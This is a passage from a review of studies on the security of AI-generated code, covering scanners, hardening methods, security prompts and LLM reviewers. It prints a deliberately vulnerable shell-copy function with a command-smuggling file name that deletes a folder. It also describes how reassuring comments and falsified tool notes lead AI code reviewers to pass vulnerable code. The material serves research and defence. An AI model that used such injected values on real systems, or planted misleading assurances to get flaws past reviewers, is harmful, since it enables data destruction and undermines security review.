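RedCode, which supplied 88% of the confirmations, is a benchmark for testing how AI agents handle risky code, so its files are dangerous on purpose. Only CyberNative consists of code that language models wrote, and that code is also vulnerable by design. The 12.69% is therefore not an estimate of how often an ordinary request to a coding assistant yields a file that passes a scan and is open to attack. Pourleyli and colleagues make the same point and add that SecurityEval, the collection closest to real programming tasks, had the lowest confirmation rate.

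The same model both proposed and verified the vulnerabilities, so an error about a weakness can affect both steps. The model may flag a harmless file and then write a test that wrongly confirms the flag. Repeating each step five times reduces random errors but not this kind, and no human analyst checked the verdicts.

A confirmed weakness may be harmless, as the weak-randomness cases show. The agent confirmed all 29 suspected cases of CWE-338 and CWE-330, nearly a quarter of the total. Python's ordinary `random` module repeats the same numbers when given the same seed, so a test that demonstrates this will succeed on any program that uses the module. An attacker who can predict the numbers can take over accounts if the program uses them to make password-reset links, but the same weakness doesn't matter in a program that rolls dice for a board game. A real attack test would have to predict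 a value that protects something. Another 27 confirmations were for programs that use too much memory or time, which is also easy to demonstrate and, in many settings, does limited harm. Code injection, which can give an attacker control of the whole machine, was suspected several times but never confirmed.

Other features of the study lower the figure. The second agent attacked only files that the first had found suspicious, so it never tried the other 419 clean files. The container had no network or outside services, which ruled out some attacks, and GPT-5.4 nano is a small model that stronger models overtook long ago. The study describes its rate as a lower bound on what attackers could do to these particular files, but also as probably too high for code from everyday work.

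The study shows more convincingly that code can pass static analysis and still be attacked than how often this happens. Pourleyli and colleagues published their attack programs so that others could rerun them. Even if half of the 83 files turned out to be false confirmations, the rest would show that a clean scan doesn't guarantee security.

### Copilot's code, scanned and read by hand

*SecurityEval Dataset* (Siddiq and Santos, 2022) describes an older comparison that used human readers to find out what scanners miss. It used 130 Python prompts covering 75 types of weakness, each the beginning of a program that a careless programmer might finish insecurely. For example, one prompt is for a function that returns a database connection, which a model might complete by writing the password into the code. Siddiq and Santos gave the prompts to GitHub Copilot, a coding assistant, and to an open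 model called InCoder, then checked the generated code with two scanners and by hand.

| Judged vulnerable | Copilot | InCoder |
|---|---|---|
| By Bandit | 14 (10.77%) | 12 (9.23%) |
| By CodeQL | 24 (18.46%) | 20 (15.38%) |
| By hand | 96 (73.84%) | 88 (67.69%) |

If the manual verdicts are right, CodeQL found at most a quarter of the vulnerable programs that Copilot wrote. Someone who relied on the scan alone would have concluded that more than four in five of all Copilot's programs were secure.

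The comparison put the scanners at a disadvantage. An alarm counted only if it matched the exact weakness that the prompt was meant to provoke, so a correct alarm under a neighbouring CWE number counted as a miss. The human readers knew which weakness to look for in each program, which helps a great deal and which reviewers rarely know. They also judged by reading and didn't attack the programs, so some of the 96 may be harmless in a real application. In one respect the test favoured CodeQL, because 36 of the 130 samples came from its own documentation. The results are also for the tools and models of 2022. Even so, the gap between 18% and 74% is probably too wide for these objections to explain fully.

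Both scanners and the human readers found more vulnerable programs from Copilot than from InCoder. Siddiq and Santos suggest that scanners may be useful for quickly comparing two models, even if they miss many vulnerabilities. This comparison works if the scanner misses about the same share of each model's mistakes, but not if one model tends to make mistakes the scanner has rules for and the other makes different ones.

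### What Veracode's pass rate measures

Veracode, which sells scanning tools, publishes the best-known ranking of models by the security of their code, and it bases the ranking on a scanner's results. The first report in the series, *AI-Generated Code Poses Major Security Risks* (July 2025), reported flaws in 45% of cases across more than 100 models.

Veracode's *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) describes a test with 80 tasks, five for each combination of four languages (Java, JavaScript, C# and Python) and four weaknesses. In each task, the model completes a function from a comment that describes what the function should do but doesn't mention security. The code passes if Veracode's own scanner finds no flaw in it.

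In July 2026, Veracode's *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* (2026) put the average at 56%, with GPT-5.5 leading at 68%. On 29 October, Veracode (2026) announced that the average had risen to 62% and that Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6-Sol shared first place with a record 73%. The announcement gives the previous high as 68%, but Veracode (2025) had reported 72% for GPT-5 Mini a year earlier. The record therefore rose by one point, which is less than the 1.25 points that one task is worth on an 80-task test.

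The rise in the average is hard to interpret too. Vonk (2026), in *AI-written code is getting safer, mostly where it was easy*, noticed that the rates for the separate weaknesses in October don't add up to the headline figure. The same is true of the two earlier editions from 2026:

| Pass rate | Spring 2026 | July 2026 | October 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Weak cryptography | 86% | 87% | 87.4% |
| SQL injection | 82% | 83% | 83.7% |
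| Cross-site scripting | 15% | 15% | 18% |
| Log injection | 13% | 12% | 12.6% |
| Mean of these four | 49% | 49.3% | 50.4% |
| Average that Veracode reported | 55% | 56% | 62% |

Each weakness has 20 tasks, so the last two rows should match. Perhaps they cover different sets of models or use different weights. The headline average rose by six points from July to October, while the mean of the four weaknesses rose by about one. Veracode had also gone from testing 11 models to 18, so part of the rise may come from added models that scored well.

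The differences between weaknesses are much larger than any change over time, and they fit what taint tracking suggests. A model can avoid SQL injection by using a standard form of query that keeps commands and data separate, and it can avoid weak cryptography by choosing a different function. Log injection has no similar standard fix, because avoiding it requires knowing whether the text came from a user and whether anything has removed its line breaks. Cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's text runs as a script in another person's browser, can often be avoided with a standard form too, which may be why it is the only weak category that has begun to improve.

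A pass rate of 73% means that Veracode's scanner found none of the flaws it was looking for in 73% of the short functions tested. The true share of secure functions could be lower, because scanners miss flaws and the test covers only four weaknesses. It could also be higher, because the test functions have no real application around them. An alarm for log injection, for example, shows at most that an attacker who controlled the logged text could insert a line break. Java scores about 30%, roughly half the rate of the other languages. Veracode suspects that models learned from old, insecure Java code, but stricter Java rules in the scanner would also lower the score.

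The test also doesn't show that the functions work. Veracode reports that nearly all of them are syntactically correct, but a function that does nothing would also be syntactically correct and pass the scan.

Veracode also has a commercial interest in the results. According to Vonk, the company's October post concludes that a mid-tier model combined with its scanner does better than a top model without one. This is nearly guaranteed when the same scanner is used to score the code, because someone has already fixed whatever it flagged. The problem gets worse once developers train or prompt models to raise their scanner scores. The ranking still has some value, since Veracode has kept the method steady since 2025 and a model that still pastes user input into database queries deserves a low score.

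### What scanners are good for

In the study by Pourleyli and colleagues, two free tools took 77 seconds to flag 701 of 1,355 files. That speed is an argument for scanners as much as against them, because a company can repeat such a quick and inexpensive scan after every change to its code. Some of the alarms were probably false, but the researchers didn't attack the flagged files, so the study can't show how many.

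A scanner also gives the same result every time the same version and rules are run on the same code, whereas the AI agents needed five runs and a vote. Each alarm includes the rule and the line of code that triggered it, so a programmer can check both and disagree. In the documentation for its competing product, OpenAI describes the product as an addition to scanners and says that scanners provide broad, deterministic coverage.

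Scanners work best on known mistakes with a recognisable form, such as a password in the source code, a call to an outdated hash function, or a request parameter that goes straight into a database query. People and language models both make these mistakes often. Teams can also add rules for mistakes that scanners miss. In the study, neither scanner reported weak password hashes, but a team can write a rule that flags any password going into a single fast hash. The scanner will then apply that rule to every file, including those that no human reads.

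## Code hardened by training or prompting and scored by scanners

Because scanners are quick and repeatable, researchers also use them to judge *hardening*, which means trying to make LLMs write safer code. Hardening methods range from retraining a model to adding a paragraph about security to its prompt. A hardened model's code may trigger fewer alarms because the method worked, but this can also happen because the code no longer does what the programmer asked for.

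### Four hardening methods, retested

Dai, Xu and Tao (2026), in *Rethinking the Evaluation of Secure Code Generation*, retested four well-known methods. SVEN puts learned numbers in front of the prompt to push the model towards secure code. SafeCoder trains the model further on examples of secure code. CodeGuard+ restricts the model's output as it is generated, and PromSec rewrites the prompt over several rounds.

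Earlier evaluations had mostly measured security with CodeQL on one set of tasks and tested whether code worked on another. Dai and colleagues measured both on the same programs. They used two mostly Python benchmarks, BigCodeBench and SecCodePLT, with over 2,000 tasks in total. BigCodeBench comes with functional tests. For SecCodePLT, they had an LLM write the tests and then corrected faulty ones by hand. They scanned the programs with CodeQL, Bandit and Bearer. For the joint score of security and function, they counted a program as secure only if none of the three scanners reported a problem.

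The researchers applied the methods to five open models, including CodeLlama-7B and Qwen2.5-Coder-7B. PromSec doesn't need access to a model's internals, so they also tried it on two commercial models from OpenAI. These are the commercial results on BigCodeBench:

| Share of programs | GPT-3.5 Turbo | with PromSec | GPT-4o | with PromSec |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No alarm from CodeQL | 99.0% | 99.1% | 99.0% | 99.0% |
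| No alarm from Bearer | 64.5% | 73.3% | 64.0% | 68.6% |
| No alarm from Bandit | 75.4% | 84.7% | 74.8% | 74.5% |
| Passes all functional tests | 50.8% | 31.7% | 60.4% | 46.2% |
| Passes all tests, no alarm at all | 32.2% | 24.5% | 37.7% | 35.6% |

PromSec made GPT-3.5 Turbo's code about nine points more secure when judged only by the scanners Bearer and Bandit. But it broke so many programs that fewer ended up both working and free of alarms.

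Among the programs that still worked, the share without alarms rose from 63% to 77%. This could happen without PromSec fixing any vulnerabilities, if it broke flagged programs more often than clean ones.

Results were no better for the open models. On BigCodeBench, every method except CodeGuard+ clearly lowered the joint score, and PromSec more than halved it for two of the models. CodeGuard+ raised the score for CodeLlama and Mistral but lowered it for DeepSeek-Coder and StarCoder. It also had an advantage, because Dai and colleagues chose its restrictions based on the weaknesses the scanners had found in the unhardened model's code.

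On SecCodePLT, almost nothing improved the joint score, but the tests may be part of the reason. Even without hardening, GPT-4o passed all the tests on only 8.7% of these tasks. Dai and colleagues attribute this to the difficulty of the tasks, but machine-written tests that require details missing from the task descriptions could have the same effect.

These models are all at least two years old, so the size of their losses is weak evidence about current models, but the scoring problem doesn't depend on the model.

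### What CodeQL let through

CodeQL passed about 99% of the programs in the table, hardened or not, which leaves almost no room for hardening to raise the pass rate. Pass rates also varied widely between scanners. After SafeCoder hardened Qwen2.5-Coder, CodeQL passed 98.8% of the model's programs, Bandit 74.8% and Bearer 65.4%.

To see which scanner was most accurate, Dai and colleagues inspected a random sample of programs that Mistral had written with SVEN. They report results for 42 programs, 21 of which they judged vulnerable. CodeQL had found 2 of the 21, Bandit 3 and Bearer 9, although Bearer had also flagged 6 safe programs.

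One of their examples shows the kind of hole that a scanner can easily miss. The task is to copy a spreadsheet to a new file and return the new file's contents. Qwen2.5-Coder originally did this safely, by reading the data and writing it out again with a spreadsheet library. Once CodeGuard+ was in use, the model copied the file with a shell command instead. In outline:

```python
def copy_sheet(source, target):
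    if not os.path.exists(source):
        raise FileNotFoundError("The file does not exist.")
    os.system(f"cp {source} {target}")
    return pd.read_excel(target)
```

This works for ordinary file names. But an attacker who can choose the target could send `copy.xlsx; rm -r data`, and the shell would copy the file and then delete the folder `data`. The check at the top doesn't help, because it only tests whether the source exists. A taint rule that starts from web requests would miss both this vulnerability and the one in `set_language`.

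Whether this function is vulnerable in a real program depends on its callers, and the same is true of many alarms. Bearer's most common alarm for the SafeCoder version of Qwen, raised 200 times, was for weak cryptographic algorithms, which are dangerous for protecting passwords but harmless for uses such as spotting duplicate files. The true share of secure programs is therefore probably well below CodeQL's 99% but could be above Bearer's 65%.

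### Deleting the feature

As far as a scanner can tell, this is an excellent way to copy a spreadsheet:

```python
def copy_sheet(source, target):
    return None
```

Without a shell command, the program raises no alarm. Dai and colleagues found hardened models avoiding alarms in much the same way. Hardening DeepSeek-Coder with SVEN removed the alarms from 69 working programs but also broke them. In 75% of these, the model had left out the vulnerable code. In another 9%, it had written junk, such as the word "task" repeated, which counts as secure because no rule matches it.

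For PromSec, the researchers found 63 such programs, and the vulnerable code was gone from 92% of them. This makes sense because PromSec keeps scanning and revising until it finds no weaknesses or runs out of rounds (Tessa, Olatunji and colleagues, 2026, *How Secure is Secure Code Generation?*). Removing a dangerous line lowers the number of weaknesses just as well as fixing it, and is usually easier.

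Deletion doesn't explain all of the damage, because hardening also broke many working programs that had no flagged code to delete. With Mistral on BigCodeBench, CodeGuard+ broke 9% of these programs and SafeCoder broke 84%. SafeCoder's extra training probably made the model worse at programming in general.

A separate test of function can miss deletion completely. The usual choice is HumanEval, a set of 164 small Python exercises that hardly ever need a shell, a database or a network. A model that learns to leave out every potentially dangerous operation will do very well on the security tasks and lose almost nothing on HumanEval. Judged by these two scores, the model looks both safe and useful, but it fails the tasks where security matters.

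Even if the security and functionality scores come from the same tasks, they don't show how many programs are both secure and working. If 80% of programs are secure and 60% work, anywhere from 40% to 60% could be both.

### What newer hardening studies measure

The 2024 paper on CodeGuard+ had shown before the retest that measuring security alone can greatly overstate a defence's value, according to *CoGate* (2026), which presents a newer hardening method. Many newer studies now score security and correctness together. *DeepGuard* (2026) uses the share of programs that are both secure and correct as its main measure. It also reports the older security rate for comparison, but warns that trivial code can score well on it.

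*Functional and Secure Code Generation with Task Vectors* (2026) also requires a program to pass all its functional tests, but uses CodeQL to judge security. Under this rule, a method can no longer raise its score by deleting the feature, because an empty function fails its tests. However, it could still raise its joint score by replacing vulnerabilities that CodeQL detects with ones it misses.

Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026) used both kinds of scoring in *Understanding and Improving Model Editing for Secure Code Generation*, so the two can be compared. They studied methods that harden a model by changing a small part of its parameters. They first measured security with CodeQL and functional correctness with HumanEval. One method, DINM, raised the security rate of Llama 3.1 8B from 68.6% to 81.2% but lowered its HumanEval score from 38.1% to 24.0%. Another method, CoSec, which uses a second,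 smaller model to steer the main one while it writes, raised the security rate slightly on average and often lowered the HumanEval score. It's hard to tell from these separate scores whether a programmer would be better off with the hardened model.

Sun and colleagues then tested whether programs both worked and raised no alarm from either CodeQL or another scanner, SonarQube. Averaged over eight models, 44.3% of programs passed without hardening, compared with 36.6% with CoSec. CoSec did worse than no hardening for seven of the eight models. Sun and colleagues' own method, SafeEdit, reached 50.3%. It edits the model for security, then trains it on ordinary programming tasks with a penalty for drifting away from the edits.

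Tessa and colleagues retested SVEN, SafeCoder and PromSec on 180 Python tasks and found that 37% to 60% of the supposedly secure outputs didn't work. They also concluded that scanners overstate security by a factor of 7 to 21. This factor partly reflects their very strict standard, under which a program had to pass its tests and satisfy CodeQL, Bandit and GPT-4o. One false alarm from any of the three was enough to fail it. The same group complains in *The Iceberg of Pitfalls in LLM-Based Secure Code Generation* (2026) that hardening studies use such different tasks and scanners that nobody can compare their gains.

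Some researchers test the code by attacking it instead of scanning it. *Toward Secure Code Generation* introduces a benchmark of 255 Python tasks, each with functional tests and attack tests. In *Security Tests as Executable Specifications for LLM Code Generation*, Liang, Gan and colleagues (2026) showed the model some tests of both kinds in advance and kept others hidden for grading. A program succeeded only if it passed all the hidden tests. Showing the model tests raised the success rate by 19.3 points on average, but lowered it in two of the nine combinations of model and benchmark.

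In another version of the experiment, Liang and colleagues ran the visible tests on the model's first attempt and gave the model a short report of the failures. The model then repaired 80 unsuccessful programs and broke none of the successful ones. It couldn't have passed the visible tests by deleting the feature, because they also checked functionality. Some programs still passed every visible test but failed a hidden one.

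### A paragraph about security in the prompt

Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, measured how adding security requirements to a prompt affects scanner findings for complete web applications. Andročec wrote 100 specifications, ranging from single-purpose tools to platforms with several user roles. Two coding agents, Claude Code (with Claude Opus 4.8) and OpenAI's Codex CLI (with GPT-5.5), each built every application twice, once from the specification alone and once with a fixed paragraph of security requirements added. Andročec then scanned the 400 resulting applications without changing their code.

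The paragraph tells the agent to follow the OWASP Top 10, a standard list of web risks. It also requires specific measures, such as keeping data separate from database commands, hashing passwords, setting secure cookies and security headers, and making sure that users can only act on their own data.

The scans covered each application's source code, its list of declared outside packages (*dependencies*), and its behaviour while running. After Andročec set aside 832 likely false alarms, 6,721 findings remained.

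| | Without the paragraph | With the paragraph |
|---|---|---|
| Findings per application, Claude Code | 20.2 | 13.2 |
| Findings per application, Codex CLI | 20.0 | 13.8 |
| High-severity findings in the applications' own code | 103 | 54 |
| High-severity warnings about dependencies | 198 | 344 |
| Dependencies per application, Claude Code | 3.2 | 6.3 |
| Dependencies per application, Codex CLI | 3.0 | 6.5 |

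After adjusting for agent, complexity and programming language, Andročec estimated that the paragraph reduced the number of findings by about a third (ratio 0.65, 95% confidence interval 0.60 to 0.71). The reduction was similar for both agents.

The reduction was about 40% for the simpler half of the specifications and 26% to 30% for the more complex half, although the data don't firmly establish this difference. The difference is plausible because most of the findings that disappeared were about settings an application needs only once, such as headers and cookies, and a larger application has more code in which other things can go wrong.

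### Login packages for applications without users

The simplest specification is for a page that greets visitors by the name they type in. The page needs no passwords or database, so most of the security paragraph is irrelevant, but an agent told to hash passwords may add passwords anyway.

Twenty of the 46 specifications for Node.js, a system for running JavaScript on a server, described applications with no users, accounts or sessions. Andročec could compare 38 pairs of applications built from these. Of the 38 applications built with the security paragraph, 36 declared a package for logins or sessions, compared with 17 of those built without it.

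Such a package can be useful, because protection against cross-site request forgery often relies on sessions. But that attack mainly exploits a visitor's login, and these applications weren't supposed to have one. A password-hashing package in an application that doesn't need passwords looks like a safeguard but protects nothing, and it adds risk because every package brings in more code that may have flaws.

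In the applications built with the paragraph, 220 of the 344 high-severity warnings came from three packages that the other version didn't declare: `bcrypt`, which hashes passwords, `connect-sqlite3`, which stores sessions, and the database driver `sqlite3`. The known flaws are in the tools that compile these packages during installation, so a reader of the application's code wouldn't see them.

Other packages do the same jobs without those tools. Twelve applications used only these alternatives and had no high-severity warnings, while the 67 that used at least one of the three packages or a similar one averaged 5.1. Andročec suggests that prompts name the packages to use. The advice is sensible, but nobody has tested it, and the twelve applications weren't a random selection.

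Andročec also points out that warnings increased less than dependencies, by a factor of 1.79 compared with 2.20 in the 86 pairs where both could be compared. The added packages were therefore no worse than usual, but the owner still has more warnings to deal with. It is unclear how much these warnings matter, because somebody who can only visit the website usually can't reach code that runs during installation.

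An earlier pilot by Andročec had found no high-severity problems at all in the versions with security instructions. It covered only twelve programs.

### Fewer findings and real security

The findings are scanner reports, and Andročec didn't confirm that any of them were exploitable. The total also counts a missing header the same as an SQL injection, so a third fewer findings doesn't necessarily mean a third fewer ways to break in. When an application goes from 20 findings to 13, the only serious one may or may not be among those removed.

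The prompt also covers some of what the scanners check. It includes instructions to use security headers and secure cookies, and about half of all findings came from a passive web scan that checks for such things. An agent that follows the prompt will score better on this scan regardless of how secure the rest of its code is. These settings are worth having, but many only limit the damage from other mistakes. For instance, a cookie setting can stop an injected script from reading the session cookie but can't prevent the injection itself.

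The fall from 103 to 54 high-severity findings in the applications' own code is better evidence, since it doesn't come from headers and cookies. These are still small numbers for 400 applications, and some of the findings may be false alarms. On the other hand, scanners rarely detect missing permission checks, so an agent that added them would get little credit.

Andročec checked whether the applications start (386 did) but not whether their features work. Deleted features could therefore explain some of the improvement here too, though probably not much, because the applications built with the paragraph had more packages and took longer to generate. Any long list of requirements might also have helped as much as the security content did, so Andročec proposes testing a paragraph of the same length as a control.

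### Why studies of security instructions disagree

Researchers have also tested whether asking for security helps. Tony, Díaz Ferreyra and colleagues tried several kinds of prompt on GPT-3, GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 (*Prompting Techniques for Secure Code Generation*, 2024). Kharma, Sabbah and colleagues did the same with five models, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5, in four programming languages (*An Empirical Evaluation of LLM-Generated Code Security Across Prompting Methods*, 2026). *RealSec-bench* (2026) tests models on code from real repositories. Deng, Fan and Meng found 70 cases in which a coding agent put a vulnerability into a real application, and had newer agents repeat the work (*Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications*, 2026).

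| Study | Task | Measure | Effect of asking for security |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tony and colleagues | 150 short programs | Weaknesses that Bandit reports | Fewer weaknesses |
| Kharma and colleagues | 200 programming tasks | Scanner findings and manual review | No significant reduction, but a different mix |
| *RealSec-bench* | Code in existing repositories | Security and function together | More code that doesn't compile, no reliable gain in security |
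| Deng and colleagues | Repeats of 70 real tasks | Whether the known vulnerability returns | From 25.7% of runs to 11.9% |
| Andročec | 400 new applications | Findings from several scanners | About a third fewer findings |

Some of the disagreement comes from differences between the tasks. An agent that builds an application from scratch has to choose its cookie settings, headers and error pages, and an instruction can change these choices. A single function has no such settings. In an existing project, somebody has already chosen them, so the agent only has to write the feature's logic. Andročec cites SusVibes, a benchmark of 186 feature requests for existing projects, where only 11.8% of the best agent's solutions were secure and hints about the vulnerability didn't solve the problem.

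The studies also use different measures. If every application went from 20 findings to 13, a study that only counted applications with at least one finding would report no change. This can't fully explain Kharma and colleagues' result, because they also measured the number of vulnerabilities relative to the amount of code. The age of their models may be a better explanation. According to Andročec, a general security reminder in the BaxBench benchmark helped only models that reason before answering, and Kharma and colleagues mostly tested older models that don't.

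The wording of the instructions also matters. The 11.9% in the table is for an agent with a reusable set of security-hardening instructions. Deng and colleagues got a lower rate, 11.0%, just by adding that the code should be "ready for production". Asking the agent to review its own changes barely helped. This seems to conflict with the findings of Tony and colleagues, who got their best results by having the model criticise and improve its code, but they used much older models and a technique that repeats the criticism.

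A longer, more professional prompt with detailed technical instructions raised the rate to 45.7%. Deng and colleagues read the records of these runs and concluded that the agent had followed the instructions more literally and used less of its own judgement about security. Andročec's paragraph was also detailed, but its details were about security. A detailed prompt may help with whatever it mentions and make the agent less careful about everything else.

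Several of these measures would count a missing feature as a success. *RealSec-bench* scored function and security together, so code that didn't compile counted as a failure, but the same code could count as an improvement in a study that only counts scanner alarms. Deng and colleagues avoided the scanner's mistakes by judging their runs by hand. However, they counted a run against the agent only if the same or a similar vulnerability came back, so an agent that never built the feature would have passed.

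## AI reviewers and the influence of comments and names

A scanner ignores the comment about security in `set_language`, but an LLM reads it along with the code. This can help, because comments often explain what the programmer intended, but it does harm if the model treats the comment as proof of what the code does.

### Two words at the top of a program

In *Don't Judge Code by Its Cover*, Moon, Hwang and colleagues (2025) measured how much surface features such as comments and names change a model's verdict. They collected 200 programming-contest problems in each of five languages (C++, Python, Java, JavaScript and Go), with one correct and one incorrect human-written solution to each, and removed all comments. Six models then judged whether each program was correct, before and after a change that did not affect what the program did.

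Adding the comment "correct code" at the top made the judges much more lenient. These are the results for Python:

| Judge | Incorrect programs accepted | With the comment | Correct programs accepted | With the comment |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 36.9% | 49.0% | 84.7% | 92.2% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 36.5% | 48.2% | 79.7% | 88.1% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 19.3% | 34.7% | 64.2% | 82.8% |
| Llama 3.1 70B | 16.5% | 41.9% | 49.0% | 83.3% |

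The judges accepted more programs, both correct and incorrect, so their overall accuracy hardly fell. For Claude and Llama it rose, because without the comment they had rejected too many correct programs. In a security review this change would make the results worse, since one accepted vulnerability can do far more harm than several false alarms.

Names mattered too, though less. When Moon and colleagues replaced variable names with 24 random letters, verdicts became more favourable in 80% of the cases they compared. For Gemini, the effect began with two-letter names and grew with length. The researchers suggest that the judges took long names for a sign of sophistication. Since the names were meaningless, the experiment can't show how a reassuring name like `safe_value` would affect the verdicts.

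Adding eight unused functions had a similar effect, raising the share of incorrect Python programs that Gemini accepted from 36.5% to 53.4%, but adding one had no consistent effect. Comments saying that an expert had written the code made little difference. Comments that misdescribed the task had the largest effect in the other direction, lowering the share of correct Java programs that GPT-4o accepted from 86.5% to 59.8%.

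Moon and colleagues tried to reduce this effect by having Gemini write test cases before giving its verdict. The "correct code" comment then raised Gemini's acceptance of incorrect programs by 6.7 points instead of 11.7. But Gemini's accuracy on the unaltered programs dropped from 71.6% to 66.75%, a loss about as large as the reduction in the comment's effect.

All of this concerns whether contest programs give the right answers, and it applies only partly to security. A contest problem specifies the required output, so the judge can check the code against it. A security reviewer seldom has a list of the attacks the code must withstand, so a reassuring comment might have more influence. But a reviewer told to look for vulnerabilities may be more suspicious from the start.

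### Notes beside the code

Zhao, Esmaeili and Fard (2026), in *Bias in the Loop*, put the cues in the judge's instructions and left the code unchanged. The judge had to choose the correct one of two answers to a programming task, with a note describing each answer. The researchers tested twelve kinds of cue on 5,352 pairs of answers, using two small open models and one of OpenAI's GPT models as judges.

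One note called the first answer a refined revision and the second an unrefined draft. With this note, the open model Qwen3-4B did better at judging generated programs when the right answer came first (76.7%, up from 67.5%) and worse when it came second (65.5%, down from 75.4%). On hard program repairs, the gain and the drop were each about 18 points. One would expect a label to matter most on these repairs, because the judge has the least other evidence.

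The cues didn't always make a judge more likely to choose the praised answer. When the first answer was right, a note that 90% of developers preferred its style made Qwen3-4B less likely to choose it. The GPT judge's largest drop, from 77.46% to 62.51%, came when it chose between unit tests after reading a note that mentioned rich formatting and engaging trivia. It would therefore be hard to remove the bias by marking down whichever answer the note praises.

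### The same code with a different security verdict

Two studies from 2026 measured such effects on security reviews directly. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) asked eight models whether pieces of code in three languages were vulnerable, varying only the text around the code. For each kind of text, they measured how far verdicts moved between a reassuring version and an alarming one. The wording of the task had the largest effect, at 33.2% on average. For example, asking a model to verify that code meets security standards is more reassuring than asking it to identify threats. An earlier verdict on the same code moved results by 23.5%, and describing the code's author as, for example, a principal security engineer or a new junior developer moved them by 18.4%.

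The alarming versions made models flag more of the vulnerable code and, by nearly the same amount, more of the safe code. Models often changed their verdict to "vulnerable" without identifying the actual vulnerability. Like the "correct code" comment, the cues mostly changed how readily the models flagged code. Vulnerabilities that take some reasoning to find were 1.3 to 2 times as sensitive to the cues as those with a recognisable pattern. The study limited each explanation to ten words, which may have kept the models from reasoning more carefully.

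Liu and Gao (2026), in *Trusting the Tool*, tested newer models with claims that the models could check. They wrote a simple analyser that lists the risky operations in a C or C++ function and the checks that protect them, and gave the reviewing model these notes with the function. Then they falsified some of the notes in ways that could be refuted by reading the function. For a vulnerable function, they might add a false assurance that line 12 contained a check, when it only returned an error code. For a function that developers had already repaired, they added a false alarm that the new check protected nothing.

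False assurances did much more damage. Compared with true notes about the same operations, they lowered the detection rate for vulnerable functions by 19 percentage points for GLM-5.2 and Kimi K3 and by 13 for Qwen3.7-Max. False alarms did not significantly lower accuracy for any of the eleven model configurations. DeepSeek's chat model became more accurate on repaired functions, rising from 67% to 79%, because it looked for the supposedly missing check and found it. In its answers, it disputed 80% of the false alarms but only 28% of the false assurances.

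The model did better when Liu and Gao asked it in a separate request to check each claim. It then refuted 76% of the false assurances, nearly the same as for false alarms (79%). A reviewer has more reason to look for a check when told that it is missing than when told that it exists. The comment in `set_language` claims that a check exists.

Most of the simple remedies failed. Printing the cited source line next to the note made no difference, even though the line contradicted the note. Presenting assurances as claims still to be verified raised accuracy by 18 points on the first set of functions, but on new functions the gain shrank to 7 points and was no longer statistically significant. Checking every claim in a separate request and then showing the reviewer the refuted ones worked better, raising the DeepSeek model's detection rate under false assurances from 54% to 66%. For a second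 model, the gain was half as large and could have been due to chance.

These notes were labelled as tool output, which may influence a model more than a programmer's comment does. Liu and Gao mention an experiment by Thornton in which misleading comments had no significant effect on frontier models. It used only 100 samples, so it could easily have missed a shift of a few points. Comments probably influence the strongest current models less than they influenced the judge models of 2025, but nobody has shown that they have no effect.

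### How sure a model is of its own code

AI reviewers would be easier to use if their confidence scores showed when they were likely to be wrong. A model is *well calibrated* if, for example, about 80% of the programs it rates as 80% likely to be secure are secure. *An Empirical Study of Security Calibration in Large Language Models for Code* (Siddiq, Rahman and Santos, 2026) tested calibration on 36,000 Python programs that three models wrote for 100 security-sensitive tasks. After writing each program, the model estimated the probability that the program was secure. The researchers then ran functional tests and attack tests, and counted a program as secure only if it passed both.

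To measure the mismatch, they sorted the programs into ten groups by stated confidence and calculated the *expected calibration error*:

ECE = Σ (*nᵢ* / *N*) × |*sᵢ* − *cᵢ*|

Here *nᵢ* is the number of programs in group *i*, *N* is the total, *sᵢ* is the share of the group that was secure, and *cᵢ* is the model's average confidence for the group. A perfectly calibrated model scores 0.

| | GPT-4o mini | Gemini 2.0 Flash | Qwen3-Coder-Next |
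|---|---|---|---|
| Secure programs | 14% | 17% | 6% |
| Expected calibration error | 0.46 | 0.25 | 0.41 |
| Programs rated at least 80% likely to be secure that weren't | 33.9% | 17.5% | 38.3% |

The last row understates the problem because it gives shares of all programs. Only 14% of GPT-4o mini's programs were secure, so even if it was highly confident about all the secure ones, at least 70% of its high-confidence programs were insecure.

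The test produced some of this overconfidence. The models were told to assume that their programs worked, but the scoring counted every broken program as insecure. When Siddiq and colleagues left out the broken programs, the error fell by 31% to 39%, depending on the model, though GPT-4o mini's was still 0.29.

They also measured confidence by the probability the model had assigned to the program's text as it wrote it, instead of asking the model for an estimate. By this measure, 85% of GPT-4o mini's programs were insecure and had a confidence of at least 80%, which is nearly all of its insecure programs. The probability reflects how closely the text resembles what usually comes next in code, and it was almost no help in judging security.

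In real repositories, where the models had to fix known vulnerabilities, 70% to 83% of the patches were insecure despite the models' high stated confidence. Many patches didn't build, which accounts for roughly half or more of the increase in calibration error, depending on the model. For patches that did build, the calibration error was still about 0.5.

The models did no better when the researchers asked them to repair programs with low confidence scores. Some of these repairs required replacing a dangerous function with a safe one, and none of the three models ever did so. They kept the original call and added validation that only made the code look secure. All three models are well behind the best ones of late 2026, so the exact figures are out of date.

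### Recognising a mistake after making it

A model can often find a vulnerability in code it has just written. In *Broken by Default*, Blain and Noiseux (2026) gave five models 89 of their own programs that a mathematical solver had shown to be vulnerable. The models identified 70 of them (78.7%) as vulnerable. Results ranged from 12 of 18 for GPT-4o to 17 of 17 for Mistral Large.

Writing and reviewing code are different tasks for a language model. When asked for a function, the model produces code that resembles the code it learned from. Blain and Noiseux point out that most C code on the internet doesn't check whether a size calculation overflows before it reserves memory, so a model that imitates this code leaves the check out too. When asked for a security review, the model draws on different material, such as bug reports and security advice.

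The reviewer also sees the complete program, whereas a model writing code commits to the early lines before it has produced the later ones. The reviewer needs to notice only one mistake, while the writer has to avoid them all. These advantages may matter more than a reminder about security, because adding security instructions to the original prompt lowered the share of vulnerable programs by only four percentage points in the same study.

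This test contained only vulnerable code, so Mistral Large may have scored perfectly by labeling everything vulnerable. A second look also helps less in practice than these results suggest. Deng and colleagues found that, in real applications, asking a coding agent to review its own changes barely reduced the vulnerabilities it introduced.

### Comments that admit a flaw

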